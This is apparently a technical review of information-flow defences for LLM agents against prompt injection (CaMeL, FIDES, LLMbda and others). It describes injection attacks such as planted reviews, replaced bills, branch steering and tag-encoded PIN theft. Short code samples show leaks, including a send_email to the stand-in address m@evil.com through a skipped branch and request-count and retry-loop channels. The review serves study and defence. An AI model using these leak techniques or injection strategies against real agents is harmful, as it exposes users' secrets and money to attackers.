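A yes-or-no answer (bool) carries at most one bit of information, a choice from a list of n items (enum) carries at most log₂ n bits, and free text (string) has no fixed limit. FIDES adds the type to the value's label. A yes-or-no answer about a public web page gets the label ((U, L), bool), meaning untrusted, public and yes-or-no. A policy can accept this label for a consequential action while rejecting free text from the same page, labeled ((U, L), string).

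In the main example, a user asks the agent to read the latest three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. The planner must learn something about the emails to decide whether to create an event or stop. FIDES handles the task in five steps.

1. The planner fetches the emails, which stay hidden in a variable.
2. It asks the quarantined model whether they contain a meeting request, and allows only yes or no.
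3. It inspects the answer.
4. If the answer is yes, it has the quarantined model extract the details of the event into another variable.
5. It calls the calendar tool with that variable, without reading the details.

After step 3, the planner's conversation contains untrusted data, so a strict policy would block the calendar call. Costa and colleagues argue that a yes-or-no answer is unlikely to deliver a prompt injection by itself, so a looser policy can allow the call. The planner could also give the quarantined model a list of actions, such as scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply or forwarding the email, and let it pick one.

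*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025) applies the same idea to a whole agent. The quarantined part may send the privileged part values of a few restricted types, but never free text. The application's designer chooses the types.

Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of their AgentDojo tests because most of the tasks didn't need it. Their attack results therefore provide no evidence about how well the exception works.

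### What a small answer can do

The capacity argument is right about instructions, because a planner that receives only the word "yes" can't receive a new command from an attacker. But the number of bits in an answer has little to do with how much harm the resulting action can cause.

In another example from Costa and colleagues, a user asks the agent to check a Paris hotel's reviews and book a room if the rating is above 4. The planner makes the reservation if the quarantined model returns "true", so a dishonest hotel owner could get the booking by planting a review that makes the model return "true". The rule that Costa and colleagues tested for hotel bookings requires a trusted call, so it should block this one, but an exception for yes-or-no answers would let it through.

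Branch steering also works through small answers, since the attacker only has to change the answer to a question already in the plan. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) reports that such attacks succeeded 94.4 percent of the time against standard computer-use agents and 89.5 percent of the time against agents with separate planner and quarantined models.

The meeting example has another weakness. The yes-or-no answer permits the calendar call, but the event's details reach the tool as untrusted data of a type that allows many more values than yes or no. Anyone who sends a convincing request can therefore choose the time and the guest list. The user often wants this, but limiting it requires a rule about the call's arguments, such as who may receive an invitation.

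Small answers also add up. A choice among eight tags carries log₂ 8 = 3 bits each time the quarantined model makes it. An attacker who controls the tags on a hundred emails controls 300 bits, enough to encode about 37 characters of ordinary text. FIDES's labels don't count this total. Combining two labels keeps the larger of the two types, so

bool ⊔ bool = bool

and a conversation containing twenty yes-or-no answers has the same type as a conversation containing one.

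The risk depends on who has to decode the bits. To receive an injection this way, the planner would have to turn a series of tags back into a sentence, which ordinary plans don't need to do. When secrets are stolen, however, the attacker does the decoding. Costa and colleagues suggest using small types for declassification as well as endorsement. Suppose a policy declassifies any choice among eight tags, and the agent puts one tag in each reply it sends. If the quarantined model can read a four-digit PIN, injected emails could make it choose tags that encode the digits. Five replies would be enough, since 8⁵ = 32,768 exceeds the 10,000 possible PINs. A policy that declassifies small values therefore needs to limit their total size as well as the size of each one.

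### Explicit endorsement in LLMbda

Garby and colleagues object that exceptions like FIDES's are hard to audit, because someone looking at a run can't tell whether a value that passed was harmless, as the designers intended, or a real leak. In LLMbda, a program must contain the word `endorse` wherever it raises a value's trust, so a reviewer can find every exception by searching for that word.

Suppose a value has secrecy level s, and the program endorses it to trust level t inside a branch labelled pc. Its new label is

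pc ⊔ ⟨t, s⟩

The secrecy level never drops, which is the basis of the insulated theorem. Endorsement has no effect in a branch that depends on untrusted data, because the join with pc adds the branch's label, so the result stays untrusted.

This rule complicates even a simple exception for tags. A programmer would naturally check that a tag is on the approved list and then endorse it. But the check reads an untrusted value, which makes the branch untrusted, and the endorsement inside it then does nothing. Garby and colleagues instead endorse a copy first and release it only if it is on the list:

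```
let w = endorse [] v in
if any (\x. x == w) tags then w else v
```

If the tag is not on the list, the program returns the original, which is still untrusted, and a later check can reject it. The programmer must fix the list in advance. If the program built the list from Slack channel names, for example, anyone who could name a channel could add text to the list. Garby and colleagues haven't yet proved a limit on how much information this construction lets through.

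One endorsement can also enable others. Suppose a program endorses a file's contents and then gives them to a model that writes code. That code runs as trusted, so any endorsement in it takes full effect, and whoever wrote the file may get more untrusted data accepted. Garby and colleagues propose a wrapper that marks each value it endorses and stops the program on any attempt to endorse that value again. Code written by a model could endorse values only through this wrapper. They offer it as a programming rule and don't formally define what it guarantees.

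*Causality Laundering* (2026) recommends that each permission to endorse a value (mark it as trusted) be auditable and limited to particular values or transformations. A permission to endorse one account number for one payment would do much less damage if misused than a general permission to endorse. The paper also argues that the component that checks a value before endorsement must sit outside the language model and resist manipulation.

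The agent that Garby and colleagues tested has fewer restrictions. Its planner writes endorsements into its plans. An attacker can't insert an endorsement, because the plan is finished before any real untrusted data arrives. However, nothing stops the planner from endorsing too much. It endorses values such as account numbers and payment amounts, which don't come from a short list. Garby and colleagues acknowledge that a capacity limit would reject the endorsements this agent needs most.

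### The cost of removing endorsement

Garby and colleagues tested how much the agent depends on endorsement by removing it and rerunning AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks three times each, without attacks. With Qwen3.7-plus, the agent completed 30 of 48 runs (62.5 percent), down from 36 (75 percent) with endorsement. With MiMo-v2.5, it completed 26 (54.2 percent), down from 31 (64.6 percent).

The 95 percent confidence intervals extend 20 to 24 points on either side of these figures, so the totals alone don't establish a drop. A drop is still likely, because three of the tasks ask the agent to read a file and then do something that requires trusted data, which is impossible without endorsement. The agent often failed two of those three even with endorsement, so removing endorsement caused fewer additional failures than it otherwise might have.

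Removing endorsement did not measurably improve security on these two models, which resisted every attack with or without it. The agent failed under attack only twice, both times with GPT-5.2. Garby and colleagues report no GPT-5.2 results without endorsement, though they note that blocking endorsement stops this attack.

### The replaced bill

The two failures came from three runs of one task, in which the agent had to pay a bill from a file whose contents an attacker had replaced. In such a task, the agent extracts the account number and amount from the file, endorses them and calls `send_money`, which accepts only a trusted recipient.

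This attack can work even if the quarantined model accurately reports the account number and amount in the new text, which only has to look like a bill. The real bill would have produced the same labels, so a rule based only on labels can't allow one payment and block the other.

FIDES failed several banking tasks because reading a file made the conversation untrusted, and the policy then blocked FIDES from acting on what it had read. Costa and colleagues count these failures as intended.

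Garby and colleagues defend endorsement here by arguing that the user authorised the agent to trust the file by asking it to pay the bill in it, and that the planner recorded this decision before reading any of the contents. This argument justifies paying some bill from the file, but it is less convincing as a reason to accept any account number that appears there. The user presumably had a particular bill in mind and didn't mean to let whoever edited the file choose the payee.

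Garby and colleagues call cases like this the "semantic limit of information-flow defences". To refuse the false bill, the agent would have to understand its contents well enough to find them suspicious. As further evidence, they cite attacks that succeeded against other systems. Two succeeded in CaMeL's own evaluation. One was this payment case. In the other, the agent quoted a hotel review, and AgentDojo counted the quoted words as a successful attack. The same kind of quotation accounts for the only failure of TACIT, which tracks permissions in a programming language's type system, and for one of the results that FIDES's creators excluded.

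This agreement among four systems is weaker evidence than it seems, because all four teams used AgentDojo and so faced many of the same tasks, and the payment case appeared in only two of the evaluations. The argument that both bills carry the same labels is stronger and doesn't depend on a benchmark.

### Evidence from outside the file

Other checks can limit the damage from a wrong value without judging whether it is true. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* proposes COBRA, which fixes in advance what each branch of a plan may do, including its web requests and tool calls. An attacker who steers the agent into a branch for closing pop-ups would gain only the permissions that branch needs. This helps less with the replaced bill, because the agent is already in the right branch and that branch has to allow a payment. A cap on the amount would reduce the loss but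 wouldn't prevent it.

A second language model could judge whether the bill looks genuine, but it would have to read the attacker's text. *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (2026) gives the example of an agent that finds the name of a software package in an online post. If a second model checks whether this is the right package, an attacker can choose a name that begins "this-is-the-right-package" and continues with an instruction.

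In SA-CUA, the system from that paper, a component that never sees the untrusted value first works out what to expect, using only trusted sources. The system then checks the value against that expectation and marks it as trusted only if the two agree. An attacker can make the check fail but can't get a value of their own choosing marked as trusted.

For the bill, the trusted source could be the bank's record of the user's earlier payments. The software could require an account the user has paid before and an amount close to the previous one, so an attacker's new account would fail the check. A loose check still lets the attacker, for example, send the rent to a different company the user has paid. Requiring an exact match prevents this, but the agent could then take the account number from the bank's record and ignore the one in the file. The first bill from a new supplier has no earlier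 payment to compare with, so the system would have to refuse it or ask the user.

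## The interpreter that tracks the data

If CaMeL's interpreter loses a label partway through the planner's program, every later policy check relies on wrong information. Garby and colleagues found two kinds of ordinary Python code that make the interpreter lose labels. One has a branch that the program skips, and the other inserts text into a string.

### A leak through a skipped branch

In their main example, an agent manages a bank account, and a program tries to tell an outsider whether the balance is above a certain amount. The direct version is one line:

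```
if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The email would reveal something about the secret balance through an implicit flow. Because the condition reads the balance, CaMeL's interpreter treats the call inside the branch as dependent on a secret and blocks it.

A program can avoid this check by changing a variable inside the secret branch and sending the email later. With the variable names that Garby and colleagues use, the program looks roughly like this:

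```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Both variables start out public. When a program assigns to a variable inside a secret branch, CaMeL makes that variable secret, but only if the program enters the branch. The table shows both possible runs.

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below the threshold |
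|---|---|---|
| Start | `tmp` is True and public; `rich` is True and public | The same |
| `if account.balance > threshold` | Program enters the branch; `tmp` becomes False and secret | Program skips the branch; `tmp` stays True and public |
| `if tmp` | Program skips the branch; `rich` stays True and public | Program enters the branch; `rich` becomes False and stays public |
| `if rich` | The email goes out | No email |

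The outsider receives an email exactly when the balance is above the threshold. When it is above, `rich` depends on the balance because the balance made the program skip the line `rich = False`. But the interpreter updates a label only when it executes an assignment, and it never executed this one, so `rich` stays public. When the balance is not above the threshold, the interpreter executes the assignment, but `tmp` is still public, so `rich` stays public in that run as well.

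J. S. Fenton described this trick in 1974, and Dorothy Denning rewrote it as conventional program code in 1976. *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (2019) calls the method that CaMeL follows here "observable tracking". When the program changes a variable in a sensitive branch, this method raises the variable's label and lets the program continue. The study notes that the method ignores hidden flows, which pass through branches the program skips.

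One email reveals only one yes-or-no fact, but a program can repeat this with a different condition each time. Twenty repetitions, one for each binary digit, would reveal any whole-number balance below 2²⁰ = 1,048,576.

An attacker would still have to get the planner to write such a program, for instance through a tool description or text that the user pastes into the request. Garby and colleagues demonstrate the flaw with a program they wrote themselves, not one that an attacker got the planner to write.

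The same gap affects trust, and an honest planner could run into it by accident. Suppose the user asks the agent to pay an invoice unless the supplier has cancelled it by email:

```
pay = True
if query_quarantined_llm(f"Is the invoice cancelled? {email}", bool):
    pay = False
if pay:
    send_money(recipient=supplier, amount=total)
```

If the quarantined model answers no, `pay` is still True and still trusted, so the payment appears to depend only on the planner's decision. An attacker can therefore get the payment through by making the model answer no. If the planner had put the payment directly under a condition that reads the model's answer, the interpreter would have recorded that the payment depends on the email. Both programs do the same thing, so in this case the user's protection depends on the planner's coding style.

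### The classical repair

The repair relies on pc, the label of the current branch, which is secret inside the branch that tests the balance. *Information Flow Control in WebKit's JavaScript Bytecode* (2014) describes it as the no-sensitive-upgrade check. It allows an assignment to a variable x only if

pc ⊑ label(x)

A program may therefore not change a public variable inside a secret branch. If the balance is above the threshold, the interpreter now stops the program at `tmp = False`. If the balance is lower, the program finishes without sending anything, so the outsider gets no email in either case.

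The interpreter has to stop the program rather than mark `tmp` as secret, because the label would then depend on the secret. In a run with a low balance, `tmp` would still be public, and the interpreter can't change its label in a run that it isn't executing. Someone who can see whether the program finished still learns one bit, which the noninterference theorem for LLMbda also allows.

The check also stops harmless programs. Suppose an agent reads a private calendar, sets a public variable `busy` to True if there is a conflict, and uses the variable only to word its reply to the user. The interpreter stops this program whenever there is a conflict, because it can't determine at the assignment how `busy` will be used later. It might also stop a program halfway through a task, after the agent has sent one of two emails. Garby and colleagues' agent first tests each plan on made-up data, but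 the test doesn't raise information-flow errors, so a plan can pass it and then fail in the real run. The program can't safely catch the error and continue, because catching it would reveal to later code that the secret branch had run.

The check isn't enough to protect the invoice payment. If the quarantined model returns "yes" for whether the supplier has cancelled, the interpreter stops the program at `pay = False`. If the model returns "no", the program never reaches that line, `pay` stays trusted, and the money goes out. An attacker who can make the model return "no" therefore still gets the payment. Termination-insensitive noninterference permits this because the untrusted result only determines whether the run finishes.

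The JavaScript study describes a different repair that handles this case, the upgrade statement, which raises a variable's label before a branch, whether or not the program enters the branch. If the planner's program marks `pay` as untrusted before testing the model's answer, the payment depends on an untrusted value in both runs, and a policy can refuse it. In the balance example, the program would have to mark both `tmp` and `rich` as secret.

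CaMeL has the whole program before it calls any tool, so software could find the variables each branch changes and insert these statements automatically. This would be harder when a branch calls a function or changes an object that several variables share. More values would also be marked secret or untrusted, so a policy might block the invoice payment even when the supplier's email is legitimate.

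LLMbda largely avoids the problem because its variables don't change once defined. A conditional produces a value, as in `let pay = if cancelled then false else true`. The interpreter gives that value the condition's label whichever branch it takes, so `pay` is untrusted in both runs. The conversation with the model can still change, so LLMbda applies a version of the no-sensitive-upgrade check there.

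### Untrusted text inside a string

The second flaw is simpler. In a footnote, Garby and colleagues report that inserting an untrusted value into a string literal in CaMeL makes the value trusted. A string literal is text written directly in a program, and Python can insert a variable's value into it:

```
recipient = f"{address}"
```

If the interpreter checks only the literal, which the planner wrote, it treats the result as trusted. A forged address for Bob could then pass a policy that requires a trusted recipient. This flaw would let the entire address through at once, while the skipped branch reveals or influences one choice at a time. Planners routinely build messages and questions from strings like this, so the flaw requires no unusual code.

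The footnote doesn't specify how widely the flaw applies. CaMeL's programs insert untrusted text into almost every question for the quarantined model, but its policies still blocked many of the banking tasks in the reruns. Some untrusted values evidently kept their labels, either because the flaw affects only certain strings or because the interpreter labels the quarantined model's answers separately.

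In LLMbda, a string built from several pieces gets their combined label. This is safe but sometimes stricter than necessary. When an example agent adds an email to its outbox, the untrusted recipient makes the stored subject and body untrusted too, although both were trusted when the policy checked them. The agent still sends the email, but any later step that reads the subject from the outbox would get an untrusted value.

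### The reply from CaMeL's side

Peters-Gill and colleagues, including Ilia Shumailov, one of CaMeL's creators, responded in October 2026. They accept that CaMeL's interpreter can miss implicit flows, particularly through assignments on skipped branches, and that multi-CaMeL inherits the flaw because it extends the same interpreter. They maintain that their security argument for multi-CaMeL is still valid, but acknowledge that the current software may not always satisfy the argument's assumption that tool data stays out of messages between agents. They call tracking these dependencies correctly "important future work".

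They also answer a criticism of CaMeL's retry loop but don't discuss the string flaw, which could matter more for multi-CaMeL. A skipped branch would normally let an attacker choose only between messages the planner had already written, while a string could carry the attacker's own words. In their first experiment, the orchestrator inserted a summary containing an injection into its message to another agent. Multi-CaMeL is supposed to reject such a message, but it would let the message through if the interpreter treated the finished string as trusted. No attack succeeded in their tests of multi-CaMeL, but the planners had instructions to pass tool data separately, so the tests may seldom have depended on the interpreter to catch such a message.

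An auditor could look for such flaws by random testing, without a proof. *Testing Noninterference, Quickly* (2014) tests the label rules of a small abstract machine this way. It uses a tool called QuickCheck to compare pairs of runs that start with different secrets and report any pair whose public results differ. The tool easily found a leak caused by a jump instruction that ignored the label of its target address. A revised rule made pc secret after a jump to a secret address, but a later jump to a public address made pc public again. The correct rule combines pc's old label with the label of the target address.

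The same method would suit CaMeL. A tester could generate short programs, run each one with two different balances and compare the emails that go out. The two-variable program would fail this test. Passing would be weaker evidence than failing, since random programs might never contain the combination that causes a leak.

### Where the tracking stops

Even a correct interpreter tracks data only through the code it runs. When the planner's program calls a tool, the interpreter passes values to software that usually carries no labels, so it has to rely on a declaration of what the tool does and what the result depends on.

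Data can lose its label when a tool stores it. Suppose an agent finds a forged address for Bob in the meeting notes, and a tool saves it to the user's address book. The interpreter has labeled the address untrusted, but the address book stores only the text. A week later, another program looks up Bob there. If the operator has declared the address book a trusted source, the interpreter now labels the forged address trusted, and the address passes the policy that would have stopped it the first time. To prevent this, the tool must store the label with the address, or the operator must treat everything in the address book as untrusted.

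A tool may also do more than its declaration states. The interpreter might treat a document converter as a function that takes a file and returns a PDF. If the converter also downloads images linked in the file, it contacts whatever servers the file names, and an attacker could put private text into those links. A policy that checks only emails and web requests made by the planner's program wouldn't cover these downloads. The operator could run the converter without network access, which protects the data even if the declaration is wrong.

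The checker that Nikolaou and colleagues built makes these declarations explicit. Its configuration lists the arguments of each tool and assigns a level of trust to each source of data. From most to least trusted, the levels are

trusted < user < untrusted < quarantined model

Text written in the program is trusted and messages from a chat channel are not. An operator can change which sources are trusted without changing the checker, so the same plan may count as safe in one installation and unsafe in another.

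CaMeL's own retry loop is also untracked. It is ordinary Python outside the interpreter, so information can pass through it from one attempt to the next without a label. Garby and colleagues see such boundaries between the interpreter and other code as a less obvious danger than mistakes in the rules for individual language features. An auditor can test a language feature with a short program, but finding every boundary requires knowing all the software around the interpreter.

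### Restricting and checking programs in advance

Restricting the code an interpreter accepts makes label tracking easier. According to Nikolaou and colleagues, CaMeL's interpreter already accepts only a subset of Python that excludes, for example, arbitrary `while` loops. Tallam and Miller propose a new language for plans, with limits on loop repetitions, simple conditions, and no functions that take other functions as arguments. They also recommend modelling the interpreter in a proof assistant and proving noninterference. They built neither the language nor the model. Their proposal is more useful than their account of CaMeL, because the paper they cite for it is a different one.

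The proposal addresses the skipped branch by putting labels into the language's types. A smaller language wouldn't fix the flaw by itself, because the two-variable program contains only assignments, conditions and a tool call, all of which the proposed language would allow.

A type checker examines a program before it runs, so it sees both branches. *Giving Semantics to Program-Counter Labels via Secure Effects* (2020) writes the basic judgement as

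Γ ⋄ pc ⊢ e : τ

Here Γ lists the types of the variables, and τ is the type of the expression e. Actions that could leak information fail this check when pc is too sensitive.

The checker rejects the two-variable program whichever types the programmer chooses. If `tmp` is public, the assignment `tmp = False` fails because it changes a public variable inside a secret branch. If `tmp` is secret, `if tmp` begins a secret branch, and `rich` must be secret as well. The last condition then begins another secret branch, and the email inside it fails.

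Any part of a program can safely create a function that sends an email, but calling that function in a branch that depends on secret data would leak information. The function's type therefore has to record what happens when a program calls it.

A checker that examines every branch must also account for the conditions. In the rules Nikolaou and colleagues describe for CaMeLoT, a value takes its level of trust from the values used to compute it. The program only ever sets `pay` to True or False, which are both trusted literals, so under those rules alone `pay` would be trusted on every path, even though the quarantined model's answer determines which path the program takes. The checker would also have to add the condition's label to every variable that either branch changes.

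### TACIT and TypeGuard

Two recent systems use the type checkers of existing languages. TACIT, by Odersky and colleagues, uses Scala 3. As Garby and colleagues describe it, a program needs a permission for each kind of outside effect, such as sending data over a network. Scala's capture checking records in a function's type which permissions it retains. The compiler can then reject generated code that would send classified data somewhere it has no permission to reach.

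TypeGuard, by Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, uses Haskell. The developer writes the code surrounding the agent, and the model's programs must type-check against that code before they run, so the same rules apply to both. For information flow, TypeGuard uses LIO, an existing Haskell library that treats labels as values a program can handle while it runs.

Both systems rely on mature compilers, which many more people have used and tested than CaMeL's interpreter. But neither separates planning from untrusted data. The model can use a tool's result to write its next program, which suits tasks that depend on what the agent finds. It may therefore write the program an attacker wants, so the types and permissions have to make that program harmless. In the reported tests of both systems, almost no attacks succeeded. Neither system has a machine-checked theorem that covers the compiler, the developer's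 code and the model together.

Unlike the no-sensitive-upgrade check, a type checker rejects a program before the agent has done anything, so the planner can try again without leaving a task half finished. However, some labels are unknown at that point. In the banking tasks, for example, the permitted reader of a payment's details is the recipient. The label identifies the recipient by account number, which the program may learn only after reading a file. A type checker needs extra rules to handle such labels, whereas an interpreter can read the number when it arrives.

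### The interpreter verified in Lean

LLMbda checks labels during the run, and its interpreter has a mathematical specification. Garby and colleagues wrote the specification, the proofs and the interpreter in Lean. They believe the interpreter is the first LLM agent runtime with machine-checked security theorems about its executable code. CaMeL has no such specification for an auditor to compare its code with.

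The noninterference theorem concerns the specification, so a second theorem has to connect the specification to the interpreter. The difficulty is that a language model's answers are random, while the interpreter in Lean is a function that always returns the same result for the same input. Garby and colleagues resolve this by giving the interpreter an extra input called an oracle, which works like a book of answers written in advance. The interpreter looks up each answer by the conversation so far and the number of answers it has already received. In symbols, the theorem states

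⟦pc ⊢ C, e⟧(C′, V) = μ({o : running e from C with oracle o ends in C′ and V})

The left side is the specification's probability of ending with conversation C′ and value V. On the right, μ is the probability of drawing an oracle o that makes the interpreter end with the same conversation and value.

For example, a program might ask a model twice to flip a coin that lands heads with probability 0.3, then return the number of heads. If the model follows the instruction exactly, the specification gives no heads a probability of 0.7² = 0.49, one head 2 × 0.3 × 0.7 = 0.42, and two heads 0.3² = 0.09. If someone fills the answer book at random, choosing heads with probability 0.3 each time, the interpreter returns each count with the same probability as the specification. The theorem establishes this match for every program in the language, so an interpreter rule that drops labels the specification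 keeps would contradict it.

The proof allows the model's responses to be malformed, but it assumes that the model answers every request and that its probabilities stay the same throughout the run. A commercial provider might violate the second assumption by replacing the model partway through a task.

The code that contacts the model is also outside the proof. It converts the conversation into a web request, sends it and returns the reply. Lean's proofs treat this code as a fixed but unknown function. If a bug added text from another conversation to the request, untrusted text could reach the planner, and the proofs would not detect the bug. This code is much smaller than a whole interpreter, so it is easier to review by hand. An operator also has to trust Lean itself and the computer that runs it.

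The tool policies leave more room for error. Garby and colleagues list policies for their banking agent that label only file contents as untrusted. Recent transactions don't get that label, although Costa and colleagues treated transaction descriptions as untrusted when they tested FIDES on the same bank. If an attacker puts instructions or a false account number in a description, the verified interpreter will carry the wrong label through the rest of the program.

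The list also omits some checks on sensitive tools. The tool for immediate payments requires a trusted recipient, while the tool for scheduled payments requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. A program could therefore schedule a payment to an untrusted account number, even though the interpreter would refuse to send money there immediately. The tool for changing the user's personal details has no check in the list. Garby and colleagues state that they deliberately simplified the policies for a proof of concept and that LLMbda could enforce stricter ones.

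In Garby and colleagues' tests, the bank was part of the program. They wrote its eleven tools as LLMbda functions that act on a record containing the user's balance, transactions and files. Python code loaded this record from AgentDojo before each run and copied the final version back afterwards. They argue that the agent couldn't tell this simulated bank from a real one, but a real bank's data can change while the agent works.

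## Leaks through loops, errors and timing

An interpreter that labels data correctly can keep a secret out of every email and web request an agent sends. But an outsider may still work out the secret from how many requests arrive, when they arrive, or whether an expected one is missing.

### Counting requests

Tallam and Miller give a very short example, a loop that runs a secret number of times:

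```
for i in range(secret): fetch("ping")
```

Each request contains only the word "ping", which is public. But whoever runs the server can count the requests in its access log, and the count equals the secret. A four-digit PIN, about 13.3 bits, would leak completely in one run.

Benign plans contain such loops too. Suppose a user wants the month's foreign invoices added up in euros, and the program fetches an exchange rate from a public site for each invoice. The site's owner learns the number of invoices but not their amounts. Costa and colleagues accept leaks of this kind in FIDES.

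The choice of requests can reveal more than their number. An agent that knows the user's diagnosis might open the websites of three specialist clinics to look for an appointment. The addresses reveal the diagnosis, even if the agent never types it anywhere. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) calls such leaks behavioral covert channels and argues that information-flow controls have difficulty detecting them. WRA, an earlier attack it cites, infers private information from the sequence of domains an agent visits.

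### Errors

When a tool raises an error that the program doesn't handle, the program stops. If the error depends on private data, so does everything that should have happened next. Suppose a user asks the agent to look up their next oncology appointment and then tell Bob that his message arrived:

```
appointment = find_appointment("oncology")
send_email("bob@example.com", "Got your message, thanks.")
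```

If the calendar tool raises an error when it finds no appointment, Bob gets a reply only when an appointment exists. The reply contains nothing from the calendar, so a policy that checks the labels on its text allows it. Bob learns one bit, provided he knows what the user asked for. If he could also see which of seven kinds of error had occurred, he could distinguish eight outcomes and learn up to three bits.

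Tallam and Miller infer the loop and error channels from attacks on processors and operating systems. They report no experiments on agents.

### Timing

An outsider who receives two messages from an agent can measure the time between them. If the quarantined model reads private attachments one at a time between the messages, and each takes about two seconds, a gap of twenty seconds suggests ten attachments. In principle, one gap can leak up to 10 bits if it can last anywhere from 0 to 1,023 seconds and the outsider can measure it to the second. If response times also vary for unrelated reasons, the outsider needs many measurements to detect a small difference.

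CaMeL's restricted Python has no clock, so a program can't time its own steps. This doesn't prevent an outside observer from timing them.

Fu, Shao and colleagues (2026) demonstrated a timing attack on an agent in *PolicySniff*, though under favourable conditions. They ran their own process on the same graphics processor as the agent's model and timed it to infer which of two approval rules the agent's prompt contained. Their balanced accuracy (the average of the accuracies for the two rules) was 94 percent. They knew both rules and the exact task in advance, and nobody else was using the processor. Their measurements raised the agent's median response time from 2.5 to 7.5 seconds, which an operator might notice. They recovered a setting rather than a user's data, but the leak arose in hardware, which an interpreter's labels don't cover.

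Network traffic is a related channel. Cloudflare's *Mitigating a token-length side-channel attack in our AI products* describes how researchers at Ben-Gurion University used token lengths to read encrypted replies from chat assistants. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* cites AgentPrint, which analyses encrypted traffic between users and agents in the cloud.

### Blocked runs

Stopping a forbidden action can reveal the fact that the policy was protecting. The previous section described a one-line program that tries to email an outsider if the user's balance is above a threshold. Here it is with a harmless second message:

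```
if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
send_email("m@evil.com", "done")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the interpreter blocks the first email and the run ends. Otherwise, the program skips that email and sends "done". The outsider can tell which happened by whether "done" arrives.

Information-flow systems usually tolerate this leak because preventing it would rule out too many harmless programs. *Reconciling Shannon and Scott with a Lattice of Computable Information* (2022) compares two loops that depend on a secret. One always ends, while the other ends only if the secret is zero or less, so whether it ends leaks information about the secret. Typical analyses can't determine whether a loop ends, so they have to reject both or, if they are termination-insensitive, accept both.

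*Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (2015) puts the tolerated leak at one bit if the outsider sees only the start and end of a run. Programs that produce output during the run may leak more. Suppose a program posts 0000, 0001, 0002 and so on in a public channel, and after each number checks whether it matches the user's PIN. When a number matches, the program tries something forbidden and the interpreter stops it, so the last number in the channel is the PIN. Agents usually act during a run, so an operator can't assume that a blocked run reveals only one bit.

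It also matters who can cause the failure. *Nonmalleable Progress Leakage* (2025) argues that an app might reasonably accept the small, unlikely leak from poor signal but still forbid a leak that someone causes maliciously.

### The retry loop around CaMeL's interpreter

CaMeL's planner can make mistakes in its programs, so a loop around the interpreter reports each error to the planner and asks for a corrected program, up to ten times. If the policy blocks a program only when a private balance is above a threshold, the planner learns from the error whether it is. The loop carries no labels, so the interpreter still treats the planner's next program as public. Garby and colleagues point out that repeating the test with new thresholds can therefore reveal the entire balance, one bit at a time.

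Suppose the balance is 700,000, and the planner knows only that it is a whole number from 0 to 1,048,575. Each test can halve the range:

| Test | Is the balance above this amount? | Result | Possible balances left |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 524,287 | Blocked | 524,288 |
| 2 | 786,431 | Not blocked | 262,144 |
| 3 | 655,359 | Blocked | 131,072 |

After ten tests, 1,024 possible balances remain, and after twenty only one does, because 2²⁰ = 1,048,576. The planner can then write "700000" into its next program as ordinary text and email it to anyone. The interpreter treats the planner's own text as public, so a policy that checks labels allows the email.

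An attacker would first have to influence the planner to do this, as with the skipped branch, because ordinary tasks don't require it. The planner would also have to make each unblocked program fail in some other way, since a successful run ends the loop. Garby and colleagues infer the leak from how the loop works, but didn't test it in their AgentDojo runs.

Error messages can also carry an attacker's words to the planner. If a tool can't find a contact whose name came from a hostile web page, and its error message quotes that name, the planner would read text from the page. CaMeL censors error reports to reduce this risk, but Garby and colleagues note that the censorship has no formal guarantee. Even an error report with all its text removed reveals that the attempt failed.

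### A limit on what one run reveals

LLMbda also allows leaks through whether a run finishes, but Garby and colleagues prove a limit on their size. Let μ(q) be the probability of a visible result q when the secret has one value, and ν(q) its probability when the secret has another. They measure how far the two sets of probabilities differ by

Δ(μ, ν) = ½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)|

If div is the probability that a run doesn't finish, then

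Δ(μ, ν) ≤ (div(μ) + div(ν)) / 2

Suppose an agent's runs fail to finish 2 percent of the time when the user's salary is low and 6 percent when it is high. The difference is then at most (0.02 + 0.06) / 2 = 0.04. If the runs always finish, the difference is zero.

The sum includes only runs that finish, but an outsider who waits long enough to conclude that a run has failed can use that failure as evidence too. Counting failure as a visible result raises the limit to the larger of the two probabilities, here 0.06. If both salaries were equally likely to begin with, the outsider could guess the right one at most 53 percent of the time, compared with 50 percent by chance.

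The limit offers little protection if failures are common. In the balance example, the run always fails above the threshold and never below it, so an outsider who notices a failure knows for certain that the balance is above the threshold. Small leaks also add up. Suppose the agent repeats the salary task a hundred times and the failures are independent. An outsider who guesses "high" after seeing four or more failures would be right about 86 percent of the time.

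A program written in LLMbda can't catch a failed label check and try again, so it can't repeat the test as CaMeL's planner can. But a user or script that restarts the whole agent after each failure creates a similar loop outside the language. The limit also assumes that outsiders see nothing until a run ends. This is true of Garby and colleagues' simulated bank, which is part of the program. With a real chat channel, the program that counts up to the PIN would have posted its numbers before it was stopped.

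### STRICT mode and loop limits

In normal mode, CaMeL treats a value as depending only on the data used to compute it, so "ping" stays public however many times the loop runs. In STRICT mode, it treats values assigned inside a loop or branch as also depending on whatever controls it, so a policy can account for the secret that set the number of repetitions. Dongol confirms that tracking data dependencies alone isn't enough for every plan. He describes STRICT mode as designed to address this but doesn't model it.

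STRICT mode doesn't fix the skipped-branch flaw from the previous section, because the interpreter still can't label an assignment it never executes. It doesn't help with the oncology appointment either, because that program has no loop or branch.

The mode also restricts ordinary tasks. Suppose an agent loops through a private guest list and writes an invitation to each guest. Every invitation depends on the list, so a policy that compares recipients with permitted readers would block invitations to guests who aren't allowed to see the list.

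Tallam and Miller suggest turning on STRICT mode automatically for any loop whose length depends on a secret. The system would then block calls that change something, or ask the user to confirm them. If fetching a web page counts as read-only, this rule would allow their "ping" example.

Tallam and Miller also suggest a fixed limit on such loops. A limit of 15 requests leaves 16 possible counts, from 0 to 15, so the count reveals at most 4 bits. The agent then can't finish a task that needs more than 15 requests. Always making exactly 15 requests, with dummy requests to fill the gaps, would hide the count completely, but this works only for harmless lookups, not for actions such as payments. They also suggest combining all the lookups into one request, which the agent can do only if the site supports it. The size of the combined request might still reveal how many lookups there were.

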